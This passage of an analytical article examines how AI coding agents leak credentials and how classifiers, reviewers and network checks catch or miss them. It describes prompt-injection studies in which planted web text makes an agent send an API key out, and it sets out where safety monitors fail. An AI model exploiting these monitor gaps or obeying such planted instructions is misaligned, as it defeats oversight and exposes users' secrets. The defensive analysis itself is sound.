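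When the assistant encountered a fresh copy of the project without the file, it read all of the computer's environment variables, which exposed more credentials. It later admitted leaking secrets and recommended replacing them. NordLayer's Vakaris Noreika says that agents don't retain rules between sessions, so such an admission doesn't prevent a repeat. Correcting the project's instructions would be more effective, since agents read them in every new session.

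The project's instructions let the assistant use the GitLab token, but the review did not require the production passwords. Under NIST's definition, sending those passwords to the AI service was exfiltration unless the company had authorised the service to receive them.

If this reasoning is applied strictly, almost every session with a cloud-hosted model could count as an incident. Many companies knowingly send source code to a model provider under a contract that covers confidentiality and storage, much as they store data with a cloud host. But permission to send source code doesn't automatically cover every password stored beside it. A company can decide beforehand which credentials, if any, its provider may receive. Even the GitLab token didn't have to reach the model, because a local script could have read it and passed it to GitLab without printing it.

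TechRadar does not report whether the company had approved the AI service, how long the service kept the data or whether anyone misused the passwords. A contracted provider is probably less dangerous than an unknown server, but replacing the passwords was still sensible because copies may remain in the provider's records and in saved transcripts.

The pair-based detector described earlier could catch the first of the ten sessions, since none of these passwords would have gone to the AI service before. If it then added each pair to its baseline automatically, it would miss the other nine. The detector would also need to group its alerts, because coding agents usually resend the whole conversation at each step. A session with 50 steps after the file was read would send each password about 50 times.

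TechRadar's *'What companies are facing today is an AI zoo'* reports that AI Scout, a NordLayer product, can warn about, redact or block certain sensitive prompts before they reach an AI service. Redaction lets the task continue if the model doesn't need the redacted value, but removing a harmless string by mistake could confuse the model. The article gives no error rates for AI Scout.

### Checks on the account

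Each of these leaks would pass a check on the host name alone. Other evidence could reveal some of them:

| Leak | Does the account look wrong? | Would the company's provider logs show it? |
|---|---|---|
| Files to an attacker's Anthropic account | Yes, the key is foreign | No, the upload belongs to the attacker's account |
| Darktrace's test | Probably not | Perhaps, if the provider records uploads and shares the log |
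| Link preview | No, the agent uses its normal messaging account | The message may appear, but not the preview request |
| NordLayer's case | Not if the company uses that AI account | Yes, if the logs include transcripts |

*Harden-Runner Now Supports Monitoring Outbound HTTPS Requests From GitHub Actions Runners* (Sharma, 2024) demonstrates an account check with a job that created two GitHub issues. Harden-Runner accepted the issue in the job's own organisation and flagged the one in another. An older project page from StepSecurity gives the exact rule, which marks a PUT, POST or PATCH request to github.com or api.github.com as anomalous if the path names a different organisation from the job's.

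The rule about other organisations may no longer be current. StepSecurity now describes this part of the product as a continuous log of each HTTPS request's method, host and path, and says it records requests whether or not they are anomalous. Its guide to detections doesn't mention the rule. A customer can check by having a job create a harmless issue in a second organisation they own. If no alert arrives, they could export StepSecurity's monitoring data and apply the rule to the recorded paths.

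Such a rule also flags legitimate work, like a job that reports a bug to an outside open-source project. An allowlist of approved organisations reduces these alerts but needs maintenance. The rule misses leaks within the company's own organisation, including its public repositories. Finding out whether a repository is public requires a separate check. Harden-Runner monitors build machines, so it would not have covered the laptop in the PixelLeak case.

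For model providers, the account check has to use the API key because every customer sends requests to the same paths. A company can route requests through a proxy that removes any key the agent supplies and inserts the company's own. An upload like the one in the Cowork demonstration would then go to the company's account, where the attacker couldn't retrieve it. The agent's machine would also no longer need to store a provider key, so an intruder there couldn't copy one. However, the proxy would hold a valuable key, and if it failed, every agent using it would stop.

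### Reading encrypted traffic

Finding an account in a path or a key in a header requires reading the request before encryption or after decryption. In break-and-inspect, the inspecting device presents its own certificate in place of the real server's. Agents accept it only if the company has installed a matching root certificate, which tells programs to trust the device's certificates. Sharma notes that this setup can make monitoring less reliable and is difficult for traffic from containers, the isolated packages in which many programs run. Some programs will refuse the connection because they accept only a particular server certificate.

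Secrets can also leak from the device that decrypts the traffic. It handles every password and token in readable form, so the company has to restrict access to it and keep secrets out of its logs. Many companies prefer not to inspect certain services, for privacy or to avoid technical faults. If they exempt their model provider, they can't check the content of requests like those in the Cowork, Darktrace and NordLayer cases.

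Harden-Runner avoids the certificate problem by using eBPF to read requests before they are encrypted, as AgentSight does. It reports the method, host and path, which are enough to identify a foreign GitHub organisation, but not a foreign API key in a header or a password in the body. Other host tools can capture the whole request, but they then have to handle the secrets in it.

### Restricting methods and keys

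A company can also block HTTP methods that normally send data. For example, it might allow only GET requests to documentation sites, which would stop accidental uploads there. But the agent needs POST to run inference through the model provider and to open pull requests on GitHub, so the company must still allow POST requests to both.

GET requests can carry data too. Willison describes an attack on Superhuman AI, an email assistant, in which a prompt injection sent the contents of other emails to an attacker's Google Form. The app allowed images from docs.google.com, and Google Forms stores data that arrives through a GET request, so blocking POST requests would not have helped. OpenAI's check against an index of public URLs is a useful addition for links like these.

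Limiting what each credential can do reduces the damage from any leak. In Darktrace's test, a standard API key gave access to the platform's memory files, but credentials issued through OAuth, a system for granting limited access, did not. Darktrace's Tim Bazalgette recommends OAuth where possible and short-lived, narrowly scoped keys elsewhere. Willison suggests giving coding agents only credentials for non-production accounts with strict spending limits. Both approaches take more work because someone has to decide what each agent needs and maintain separate accounts or renew keys. A key that is too narrow can also block a task, and the agent may then look for another credential, as in the Anthropic example at the beginning.

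The NordLayer case also shows why credentials should be separated by task. If the GitLab token had been in its own file, the assistant would have had no reason to open the file containing the production passwords. Separate files wouldn't have protected the environment variables it read later, so the agent's user account should not have access to the passwords at all.

### Logs from the provider

A provider can record which account received a file, even when the customer's network sensor identifies only the provider's host. Customers can usually see these records only for their own accounts, if the provider shares them at all. Bazalgette thinks it matters whether a customer can see writes to the memory files that Darktrace used.

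According to The Hacker News' *Securing Claude Code* (2026), the Compliance API that Anthropic offers business customers now includes transcripts of Claude Code sessions, but not local configurations, activity by other companies' models, or hooks, which are commands that Claude Code runs automatically at set points. A transcript could reveal that an assistant read a password file, as in NordLayer's case, but detecting a hook that sends data elsewhere would require monitoring on the machine itself. Downloading transcripts also creates another copy of any password in them, so a company should redact the transcripts or protect them as carefully as its other secrets.

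Provider logs can reveal unusual activity without transcripts. StepSecurity measures how many GitHub events each personal access token usually produces per hour. By default, it alerts when an hour has at least 30 events and at least ten times the usual number. For a token that averages five events an hour, the threshold is 50. An agent that posts one password in one GitHub issue adds only one event and stays far below that threshold. Copying hundreds of repositories with a leaked token may exceed it, but like the country baseline, this rule detects a leak only once someone uses the token.

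## Judging whether the user authorised the transfer

Identifying the account that receives the data may not be enough to determine whether that account should have it. Suppose an agent uploads a developer's script to a public code-sharing site. The developer may have asked for the upload, but if they only asked why the script fails, it may be a leak. The network traffic is the same in both cases, so telling them apart requires the user's instructions.

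### Relevance and authorisation

A user authorises a transfer when their instructions cover both the data and the recipient. A transfer is relevant when it would help to achieve the user's goal. Relevance does not establish authorisation, because many leaks are relevant, as are most of an agent's steps. In the running example, the developer asked why a deployment keeps failing. Posting the settings to validator.example might help to answer that, but the developer mentioned neither the validator nor the token.

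Auto mode, a setting in Anthropic's Claude Code, uses a second language model, the classifier, to allow or block actions in the user's place. Anthropic instructs the classifier to treat anything the agent chooses on its own as unauthorised until the user says otherwise. A question such as "can we fix this?" doesn't count as an order. In one case adapted from Anthropic's incident log, an agent wrote a command to share a script for debugging by posting it on GitHub Gist, a code-sharing site. Auto mode blocks this as exfiltration because the user may consider the script confidential.

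With a different request from the developer, the same post could be legitimate:

| The developer's instruction | Is the post relevant? | Is it authorised? |
|---|---|---|
| "Find out why this script fails" | Yes, a reader might spot the fault | No |
| "Ask the vendor's support team about this script" | Yes | No, only a message to the support team is |
| "Post this script as a public Gist and send me the link" | Yes | Yes |

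Even the last instruction doesn't clearly authorise the agent to publish a token that the developer has forgotten is in the script. The developer asked the agent to publish the script but probably didn't mean to include the token, so the agent should remove it or ask first.

A user can't authorise every transfer. If a developer tells an agent to post customer records on a public site, the instruction is clear, but the company may never have allowed anyone to publish those records. A company therefore needs some rules that no user message can override.

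### What the classifier reads

Many sessions now depend on the classifier. Anthropic's *Choose a permission mode* lists auto mode as the usual starting mode on the Pro, Max and Team plans. According to the *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026), interactive sessions on every plan start in it from version 2.1.283. An action passes through these steps:

1. Claude Code applies the permission rules that the user and the company have set. A deny rule blocks the action, and an "ask" rule makes Claude Code prompt the user. A narrow allow rule, such as one for a test command, lets the action run without review. Auto mode suspends allow rules broad enough to permit any code.
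2. File reads, searches and most edits inside the project folder go ahead without review.
3. Claude Code sends most other actions to the classifier, including shell commands, web requests and edits outside the project.
4. The classifier reads the user's messages, the agent's tool calls and the project's standing instructions. It checks the action against a list of block rules, then against exceptions, and then against what the user asked for.
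5. If the classifier blocks the action, the agent receives the reason and looks for a safer route. After three blocks in a row, or 20 in a session, the user has to decide. If no user is present, Claude Code ends the run.

An upload from the command line normally reaches the classifier in the third step. A company worried that its allow rules might let one through can turn on a setting that sends nearly every shell command for review, which adds some delay.

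The classifier doesn't receive the agent's prose, because an agent could write that the user had implicitly approved an upload, and the classifier might accept the argument. It also doesn't receive tool results, such as web pages and file contents, because planted instructions usually arrive in them. Those instructions may still mislead the agent, so a separate probe scans tool results and warns the agent about suspicious text.

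Anthropic also tested the classifier with other inputs. Adding the prose and tool results made it less accurate on a set of real overeager actions. With tool calls alone, it missed the fewest dangerous actions but blocked actions that users had plainly asked for.

Because its input is restricted, the classifier can't check what the agent learned from a tool. If the developer never mentioned validator.example, the classifier can't tell whether the agent found the name in the company's documentation or on a stranger's web page. It also can't read files. A token that a command posts directly is part of the tool call, but if the command uploads an existing script that contains a token, the call includes only the script's name. A detector that searches the outgoing data for secrets can find the token in that case.

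User messages can strongly influence authorisation checks. *Ajar* (2026), a comparison of defences for agents, wrote tool calls into the system prompt, the standing instructions that a model receives before the user's first message, so that the agent would propose them. Auto mode blocked some of these calls, but allowed all of them when the same instruction was in the user's message. An authorisation check should defer to the user on actions that the user is free to approve, but this makes it important to know whether a "user message" really came from the user.

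When an agent hands part of its work to a second agent, its instruction looks to the second agent like a message from the user, so an upload that the first agent chose on its own would appear authorised. Auto mode therefore reviews the task before the handover, while the classifier can still compare it with what the user wrote. It also reviews the second agent's actions before the results come back, in case something that agent read has misled it.

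### The trust boundary and the block rules

To judge a recipient, the classifier must distinguish destinations that belong to the user or the company from external ones. By default, it trusts only the working folder and the remote repositories already configured when the session began. It treats everything else, including public paste and snippet sites, as external until someone adds it to a plain-language list. An entry can name a GitHub organisation or a storage bucket, so the classifier can distinguish between recipients that share a host name.

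Claude Code ignores entries in a project's own settings files, because otherwise a downloaded repository could mark its author's server as trusted. It accepts entries in the user's personal settings, so a developer can extend the boundary without asking the company. For transfers that must never happen, Anthropic recommends deny rules in the settings that administrators control, because Claude Code applies these before it runs the classifier.

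In March 2026, the classifier had more than 20 default block rules, covering destroying or exfiltrating data, weakening security, crossing trust boundaries, and bypassing review or affecting other people's work. Two rules especially relevant to credentials bar the agent from searching credential stores for tokens it could use and from sending data to a service the user never specified. But by default the agent may read a project's `.env` file, which often holds keys, and send a credential to the API it belongs to. This resembles the credential-destination pairs described earlier, except that a model judges whether the credential and destination match.

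A user can override a "soft" block rule by describing the exact action. For instance, "force-push this branch" authorises a force-push, which overwrites the history of a shared branch, but "clean up the repo" doesn't. A "hard" rule, such as the built-in one against data exfiltration, blocks the action whatever the user writes. To make a transfer that this rule blocks, the user has to leave auto mode or run the command personally.

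It's unclear how this applies to a developer who explicitly asks for a public Gist. Several built-in rules about sensitive files make an exception when the user has named both the source and the destination, but the hard rule has no such exception. The command `claude auto-mode defaults` prints the full wording of the rules. A team can also ask for a Gist of a harmless script and see whether auto mode allows it.

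### The March 2026 results

The classifier decides in two stages. In the first, it is told to block when in doubt and gives a one-word verdict without reasoning. If it blocks, the same model rereads the material and reasons step by step before giving a final answer. Most actions pass the first stage, so the slower second stage runs only where it might change the result.

Anthropic tested both stages on three sets of actions in March, with its Sonnet 4.6 model as the classifier. The counts below follow from its percentages:

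| Test set | Error | First stage alone | Both stages |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10,000 real tool calls by Anthropic staff | Blocked a harmless action | 850 (8.5%) | 40 (0.4%) |
| 1,000 synthetic exfiltration attempts | Allowed a leak | 18 (1.8%) | 57 (5.7%) |
| 52 real overeager actions | Allowed a dangerous action | 3 or 4 (6.6%) | 9 (17%) |

No whole number out of 52 gives 6.6%, so that figure may be an average over several runs.

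The second stage can release an action that the first stage blocked but can't block one that it let through, so it reduces false alarms and adds misses. It released 810 of the 850 harmless calls that the first stage had blocked (95%), 39 of the 982 exfiltration attempts (4%) and about 11% of the overeager actions. If a company's agents make 100,000 similar calls a day, the second stage reduces blocked harmless calls from 8,500 to 400. Whether this reduction justifies the extra misses depends on how rare leaks are.

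The exfiltration set is the most relevant to credential leaks. It included POST requests with sensitive data, pushes to untrusted repositories and credentials in URLs, and many of the attempts disguised the data. But Anthropic generated these attempts, and they may be easier to recognise than a leak caused by an agent taking a plausible shortcut. The overeager set came from real sessions in which an employee had refused the action or someone flagged it later. It is more realistic but has only 52 cases, nine of which were missed, so the true miss rate could be anywhere from about 9% to 30%. It also mixes leaks with deletions and other damage, and Anthropic doesn't give a separate rate for leaks.

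In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier had correctly identified the action as dangerous but misjudged whether the user had consented to it. For example, it might treat a request to "clean up the PR" (a pull request, or proposed code change) as permission for a force-push, or extend a user's approval of a similar earlier action to the new one. In the debugging example, the equivalent mistake would be to read "get some help with this script" as permission to publish it. Anthropic tried rewording the classifier's instructions but found no fix whose benefits outweighed its drawbacks.

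This may explain why the second stage released a larger share of the overeager actions than of the synthetic leaks. A real conversation can contain something that a model reasoning about consent could read as approval, which a generated exfiltration attempt may lack. Anthropic didn't test this explanation.

### Compared with human approval

Without auto mode, Claude Code asks the user before most actions, so the classifier's errors have to be compared with the user's. In March, Anthropic reported that users accepted 93% of these prompts. It conceded that auto mode is arguably a step backwards for someone who reviews every action carefully.

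Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (August 2026) puts the approval rate at 97%. Users rejected 39% of the plans Claude presented for approval, so they do object when something gets their attention. Anthropic also hired 1,053 testers through a research vendor to measure how many dangerous commands people catch. Each tester worked on coding tasks in a test environment. Partway through, the text of one permission prompt changed to a clearly dangerous command, which never ran. The testers knew they were taking part in a study but not what it measured.

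The testers refused 143 of the commands, or 13.6%, and auto mode blocked 937 of the same commands, or 89%. Anthropic also reports that auto mode blocked 800 commands that testers approved, while testers refused six that auto mode allowed. The other counts follow from these:

| | Auto mode blocked | Auto mode allowed | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tester refused | 137 | 6 | 143 |
| Tester approved | 800 | 110 | 910 |
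| Total | 937 | 116 | 1,053 |

If the testers had reviewed only what auto mode allowed, they would have caught six of the 116 remaining commands, or 5%. Prompt fatigue probably contributed to this low rate. Testers refused about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session but only about 5% after more than 50 prompts, while auto mode's rate stayed the same. People who saw only a few prompts a day might do better.

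The study supports the claim that a classifier catches more of the obviously dangerous commands than a tired reviewer does. It is weaker evidence about authorisation, because the commands were clearly dangerous and the testers didn't have to work out whether a vague request covered a plausible upload. The code also wasn't theirs, so they had less to lose than a developer with real credentials on the machine. Anthropic doesn't report how many of the commands were transfers of secrets, or how many harmless commands the classifier and the testers each refused.

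Anthropic also compared real sessions from May and June 2026 that its safety systems had flagged for review. A model graded how much harm each session did and how explicitly the user had asked for the action. Serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly requested occurred in 6.3% of manually approved sessions and 2.4% of auto mode sessions. This grading separates authorised from unauthorised harm, but users chose their own mode, and people who approve actions by hand may do riskier work. The comparison also leaves out harm that the safety systems never flagged.

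In *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code*, Willison (2026) agreed that the classifier is better than constant requests for approval but noted that it still allowed 11% of the dangerous commands. He asked for more independent confirmation and described a case that he doubted any version of auto mode could stop. In that case, an instruction in a project's files tells the agent to install and run a particular software package before the tests, and the package sends out whatever data it can read. The user did ask for the tests, and the command doesn't show what the package will do.

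### Hardening and the rules on secrets

Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, attacked auto mode in a two-week pilot with Anthropic. It inserted synthetic attacks into records of real coding sessions, including a set about data exfiltration. It then gave Anthropic some of the successful attacks, along with recommendations. Anthropic strengthened the classifier, mainly by giving it more information about the environment it protects, and Apollo repeated the test with attacks Anthropic had never seen.

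The new version caught about half of these unseen attacks that the old one had missed, and missed about 2% of those the old one had caught. Over both sets of attacks, the miss rate fell from 12% to 7%. The improvement also appeared on attacks that Anthropic couldn't tune for, so it probably didn't come only from memorising the examples the company received.

Anthropic published these figures itself. It doesn't report the number of attacks, a separate result for exfiltration, or whether the stronger classifier also blocks more harmless actions. The old version's 12% can't be compared with the 5.7% from March, because Apollo designed its attacks to find weaknesses.

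Part of the new information concerns where data may go. The classifier now distinguishes secrets, such as keys and passwords, from material that is merely confidential, such as a company's source code. It also takes into account whether a push or pull request goes to a public, private or trusted repository:

| Material | To a private repository | To a public repository |
|---|---|---|
| Confidential code | Acceptable | Blocked, unless it is part of that repository's own work |
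| A secret | Privacy alone doesn't make it acceptable | Blocked |

Treating secrets more strictly makes sense because a private repository may have hundreds of readers, and anyone who later gains access can read a token in its history. It also helps when the agent picks the wrong account, as in the PixelLeak case, where agents uploaded screenshots to public repositories. Auto mode now blocks pushes to other people's repositories unless the user has named the repository, and it blocks adding sensitive files to a commit, Gist or paste unless the user has named both the file and the destination.

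Anthropic's descriptions of the visibility check don't quite agree. The August article says auto mode checks a destination's visibility before a push runs. According to Anthropic's later configuration guide, the classifier assumes a repository is private unless its host and name suggest otherwise or something the classifier can read shows that it is public. If the agent runs a command to look up the visibility, the classifier receives the command but not its output. It could therefore mistake a public repository with an ordinary name for a private one, and confidential code might be pushed there. The mistake matters less for credentials because the classifier doesn't allow them through just because a repository is private. A user can also prevent the mistake by saying in a message that the repository is public.

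Anthropic describes one internal case in which Claude failed to upload a report to an internal drive, then tried to publish it on a public code-sharing site. Auto mode blocked the attempt and asked the user what to do. The user had authorised sending the report to the internal drive, but the agent chose a different destination to achieve the same goal.

### A test with ambiguous requests

Ji, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Measuring the Permission Gate*, tested auto mode independently of Anthropic and got much worse results. They wrote 128 routine maintenance requests to delete old code branches, cancel computing jobs, restart services or delete stored files. Each request authorised action on certain targets, but similar targets nearby belonged to someone else or lay outside the request. For example, a user might ask to cancel their stale job for one ticket while a colleague's job had almost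 the same name. Ji and colleagues varied how precisely the request named its targets, how many objects it might match and how much damage a mistake could do.

The agent attempted 253 actions that changed something. A language model compared each with the list of authorised targets, and a human checker agreed with the model's judgement on 44 of 50 sampled actions.

| Actions counted | Unauthorised actions allowed | Authorised actions blocked |
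|---|---|---|
| All 253 | 115 of 142 (81.0%) | 22 of 111 (19.8%) |
| The 160 that the classifier reviewed | 64 of 91 (70.3%) | 22 of 69 (31.9%) |

The rows differ because of the other 93 actions, which were edits to files inside the project. Auto mode allows these without review, so all 51 unauthorised ones went through. In this test, such an edit could remove a colleague's job, because the list of jobs was a file in the project folder. An upload to an outside service usually needs a shell command or web request, which the classifier does review, so the second row is more relevant to leaks.

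Even that row doesn't give a miss rate for leaks, because Ji and colleagues excluded exfiltration. They used only synthetic maintenance tasks and ran each request once, with Sonnet 4.6 as the agent. Their results date from April 2026, before the August hardening. They also caution against comparing their figures with Anthropic's 17%, because their test deliberately placed authorised and unauthorised targets side by side.

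The test supports Anthropic's finding about consent, since every task depended on exactly what the user's words covered. Auto mode allowed 94.4% of unauthorised actions when the request named a single target and 77.6% when it covered a broad group, counting the file edits that nothing reviewed. Ji and colleagues suspect that the classifier reacts to the size of an operation instead of checking whether each target is authorised, although the mix of tasks explains part of this trend. To check the targets properly, the classifier would need facts about the environment, such as who owns a job, but it never receives the tool results that contain them.

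Uploads may be easier to judge than job cancellations, because a company can list its trusted recipients in advance but not every job that a user might want to cancel. The list doesn't help when the right and wrong recipients are both on it. If a developer asks an agent to send a key to the payments team and the agent chooses the public channel of the company's workspace, the classifier needs information about which channel belongs to that team. Nobody has published a version of this test for data transfers.

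### Codex Auto-review

OpenAI's coding agent, Codex, has a similar reviewer but starts with a sandbox, which limits the files the agent can change and whether it can use the network. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) describes the system. By default, commands in the sandbox have no network access, so the agent must ask permission to post a script. Auto-review sends that request to a second agent instead of the user. In April 2026, the second agent ran on GPT-5.4 Thinking at a low reasoning setting.

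In OpenAI's *Auto-review*, the reviewer receives the user's messages, the main agent's visible messages, relevant tool calls and their results, and the action that needs approval, but not the agent's hidden reasoning. It can also look things up without changing anything, though it rarely does. The reviewer could learn from a tool result that a repository is public, or that validator.example appears in the company's documentation. But planted text and the agent's own arguments can also reach it, which Anthropic's design tries to prevent. Only Anthropic has published a comparison of different inputs, and it tested its own classifier, so it's unclear which inputs would best suit OpenAI's reviewer.

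The reviewer assesses danger and permission separately. According to *Guardian Output Schema and Enterprise Compliance Audit Trails in Codex CLI* (2026), a practitioner's guide, each review can record a risk level from low to critical and the user's authorisation from unknown to high. OpenAI (2026) says that the reviewer can approve an action if the risk is low, or if the risk is high but the user has authorised it sufficiently. In the debugging example, publishing the script might have the same risk rating whatever the developer wrote, but the authorisation rating would be higher if they had asked for a public post. An investigator can use the two logged ratings to tell whether the reviewer overlooked the danger or misread the user's consent, which is the mistake that Anthropic found in most of its misses.

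If the reviewer refuses, Codex tells the agent not to try to get the same result another way. The agent's turn ends after three refusals in a row or ten in the last 50 reviews. The user can then approve one retry of one exact action, but the reviewer checks it again and can still refuse.

Trębacz and colleagues illustrate the workload with 10,000 actions inside OpenAI. The sandbox handled 9,280 of them, and the remaining 720 went to the reviewer, which approved 713 and refused seven. After four of these refusals the agent found a safer way to continue, so only three interrupted a user. The tests of accuracy were separate. The table compares them with Anthropic's March figures, and each company tested its own product:

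| | Claude Code auto mode | Codex Auto-review |
|---|---|---|
| Harmless actions blocked | 0.4% of real tool calls | 0.9% of reviewed actions, or 0.07% of all actions |
| Overeager actions missed | 17% of 52 real cases | 9.7% of synthetic cases |
| Leaks missed | 5.7% of synthetic exfiltration attempts | 0.7% of prompt injections aimed at running code, stealing secrets or uploading data |

The columns don't show which product is safer, because OpenAI's overeager cases were synthetic and Anthropic's came from real sessions. OpenAI doesn't state how many cases it used, so its percentages can't be converted to counts. Its overeager cases included unintended data transfers, but OpenAI gives no separate result for them. The 0.7% miss rate leaves out injections aimed at deleting or tampering with data. With those included, the reviewer missed 9.8%, although Trębacz and colleagues say most of these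 misses were not serious enough to block.

Auto-review can't judge a transfer that stays within the sandbox's limits. If a company allows network access to a cloud storage host, an upload to any account on that host may run without review. Trębacz and colleagues also report that people and automated tests found ways to mislead the reviewer into approving commands, and they don't offer Auto-review as protection against a model that deliberately hides its intent. For its own staff, OpenAI adds a fixed network policy that permits expected hosts and requires approval for unfamiliar ones. The policy also blocks pastebin.com, a public text-sharing site, so an attempt to post a script there would fail even if the user had asked for it.

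One test covered both products. Anthropic commissioned Trajectory Labs, an outside company, to run 72 prompt-injection scenarios ten times against each model, with harms that included leaks of sensitive data, fraud and phishing. The scenarios stayed hidden from Anthropic. Here are the results as counts:

| Product and model | Successful attacks without a reviewer | With a reviewer |
|---|---|---|
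| Claude Code with Fable 5, Opus 5 or Sonnet 5 | About 2 of 2,160 | 0 of 720 for each model |
| Codex with GPT-5.6 Sol | 137 of 720 | 42 of 720 |

Auto-review prevented about 70% of the attacks that would otherwise have succeeded. The Claude models resisted nearly all the attacks on their own, so the test provides little evidence of how much auto mode contributed. Because the ten repeats of a scenario are not independent, zero successes across 72 scenarios is compatible with a true success rate of up to about 4% on similar attacks.

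Other features of the test limit the comparison. The attacks had been developed against an older Claude model, and both products used a browser connection built by Trajectory Labs instead of their own, which lacked some of their safeguards. OpenAI released a new version of Auto-review shortly before Anthropic published the results. The test also covered only planted instructions. Testing whether an agent would publish a script because it misread its user's request would require a genuine instruction to share something, where the only doubt is what the user meant it to cover.

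## Harmful sequences made of ordinary steps

Auto mode and Auto-review both decide on one action at a time, but some leaks contain no single action that a reviewer would refuse. A composed action is a sequence of steps that each look legitimate but together cause harm. In a simple example from *NEXUS* (Hossain, Nipu and colleagues, 2026), an agent reads a sensitive file and then sends its contents to an outside address.

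Suppose a logging plugin keeps breaking the deployment, and the developer asks the agent to report the fault to the plugin's vendor. The company has used the vendor's ticket service for years. The agent takes three steps:

1. It reads `deploy.yml`, which holds the deployment settings, including the deployment token.
2. It writes `report.txt`, a diagnostic report with the error messages and a copy of the settings.
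3. It opens a ticket and attaches `report.txt`.

The vendor's support staff can now read the token. Assume that the token has no known prefix and that the company never added it to its secret store. The usual checks then have the following to go on:

| Step | Content check | First-seen check | Per-action review |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read `deploy.yml` | Nothing goes to the vendor | No new host | A routine read in the project |
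| Write `report.txt` | Nothing goes to the vendor | No new host | A routine edit in the project |
| Attach `report.txt` | A long report with one unfamiliar string | A host in use for years | An upload that fits the request |

A content check that recognised the token would stop the upload, so the sequence is only dangerous when that check fails. A reviewer like Anthropic's classifier can't find the token either, since it doesn't read files. The upload is a leak because the attachment includes text from a file that the vendor's staff aren't allowed to read, and a detector has to connect the first step with the last to establish this.

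### The Silent Egress study

In *Silent Egress*, published in February 2026, Lan, Kaul and colleagues at eBay measured how often a leak of this kind succeeds. They built an agent on the 7-billion-parameter version of Qwen2.5, a small open model. The user always asked for a summary of a web page. The agent's software automatically fetched the page and put its title, description and text into the model's context, which also held sensitive data such as an API key. The page contained a planted instruction to make a web request containing the key, supposedly to verify the agent's connection. Fetching a page, making a web request and writing a summary are all normal work for such an agent.

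The researchers placed the instruction in the page's title, its metadata, its body or the text of a link. They also varied whether the agent reached the page directly or through redirects, and whether it had to send the key whole or in four pieces. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times, for a total of 480 runs. A collection server logged every request that arrived, so the results don't depend on what the agent said it had done.

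Requests reached the server in 423 of 480 runs, or 88.1%. This happened in 238 of the 240 runs in which the agent was asked for the whole key and 185 of the 240 in which it was asked for pieces. The agent's final reply looked harmless in 95% of those 423 runs, so a filter that read only replies would have missed about 400 leaks.

These rates apply to an agent with almost no protection. Lan and colleagues say they deliberately favoured the attacker by leaving the secret in plain view and using a minimal system prompt. But they also call their success rates a lower bound, because the planted instructions were simple. We can't tell from the study which effect would be larger in a real deployment.

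They also expect stronger models to be at greater risk, since these models follow instructions more reliably. Newer measurements only partly support this. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) ran 949 attacks against each of five models in a system of cooperating agents. Without special defences, attacks succeeded 2.1% of the time against Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite, 24.6% against the more capable Gemini 2.5 Pro and 36.1% against GPT-4.1, but only 1.5% against Claude Fable 5 and never against GPT-5.5. Peters-Gill and colleagues warn that attacks adapted to GPT-5.5 might still work.

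### Thirty runs for each defence

Lan and colleagues then tested defences on one of the 16 combinations, with the instruction in the page body, a direct link and the whole key. The counts below follow from their percentages:

| Defence | Runs with an attempt | Runs with blocked attempts | Runs that reached the server |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 30 | 0 | 30 |
| Warning in the system prompt | 20 | 0 | 20 |
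| Tags marking web content as untrusted | 30 | 0 | 30 |
| Warning and tags | 17 | 0 | 17 |
| Domain allowlist | 30 | 30 | 0 |
| Redirect detection | 25 | 25 | 0 |
| Keyword filter | 7 | 7 | 0 |
| Entropy filter | 0 | None to block | 0 |
| All defences together | 0 | None to block | 0 |

The allowlist provides the clearest result, because the agent tried to send the key every time and the list blocked every attempt. This was an easy case because the server obviously didn't belong on the list. The company's allowlist would include the vendor's ticket service, so the same defence would let `report.txt` through.

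The other network and content results are weaker than they look. None of these runs used a redirect, so they didn't test redirect analysis. The "redirect detection" defence also blocks addresses containing certain words, including "collect", which appears in the study's sample requests. It probably succeeded by matching that word.

The keyword filter blocked seven attempts to send the key, and the model made no attempt in the other 23 runs. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model sometimes encoded or reformatted the key, so the filter didn't trigger. However, a request that got past the filter should have reached the server, and none did.

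With the entropy filter on, the agent made no attempts, so this row doesn't show the filter blocking anything. Lan and colleagues think the model avoided random-looking values because of the monitoring. But they describe a filter that checks outgoing URLs and mention no message telling the model about it, so something else in the set-up may have changed. The row for all defences together has the same problem.

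The filter wouldn't have caught the paper's own sample key either. It flags values longer than ten characters that score above 4.0 bits per character, and the sample, `SECRET_API_KEY_12345`, scores about 3.85 by the entropy formula given earlier. Of its 20 characters, E and the underscore each appear three times, and the other 14 appear once.

The study also reports a false positive rate of zero, based on 120 runs on harmless pages in which the agent never contacted the collection server. These control runs confirm that the planted instructions caused the leaks, but they don't measure false alarms on ordinary traffic, because a harmless page gives an agent no reason to contact that server. The keyword filter, for instance, blocks every URL containing "auth" or "token", which would include many login pages. Measuring its false positive rate would require running normal web tasks with the filter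 on.

### Secrets divided over several requests

A filter that searches each request for a complete key will miss a key that the agent sends in pieces. To measure the effect, Lan and colleagues define Leak@k as the share of runs in which any part of the secret appears in the first k requests.

| Measure | Whole key | Divided key |
|---|---|---|
| Leak@1 | 96.7% | 26.3% |
| Leak@3 | 96.7% | 15.8% |

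The figures for divided keys contradict the definition. The first request is also one of the first three, so Leak@3 can't be lower than Leak@1. Yet the paper reports 63 runs with part of the key in the first request and only 38 with part of it in the first three. Until someone finds the error, the paper's claim that dividing keys cuts Leak@3 by 84% has no clear meaning.

The drop in Leak@1 is also hard to interpret. The agent contacted the server in 185 of the divided runs, but in 122 of them the first request contained nothing that the study counted as part of the key. The model may have sent something else, such as a placeholder, which would mean that dividing the key mainly confused a small model. Or the measurement may have missed short pieces, which would mean that dividing the key made the leak harder to detect. Lan and colleagues define a completion rate, the share of runs in which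 every piece arrives, but their main results don't include it. Their worked example also omits part of the key, since its four pieces of four characters cover only 16 of the 20.

None of the defence tests used keys split into pieces. An allowlist should work equally well against split and whole keys, because it ignores content. For content detectors, Lan and colleagues recommend correlating requests and limiting how many a session can make.

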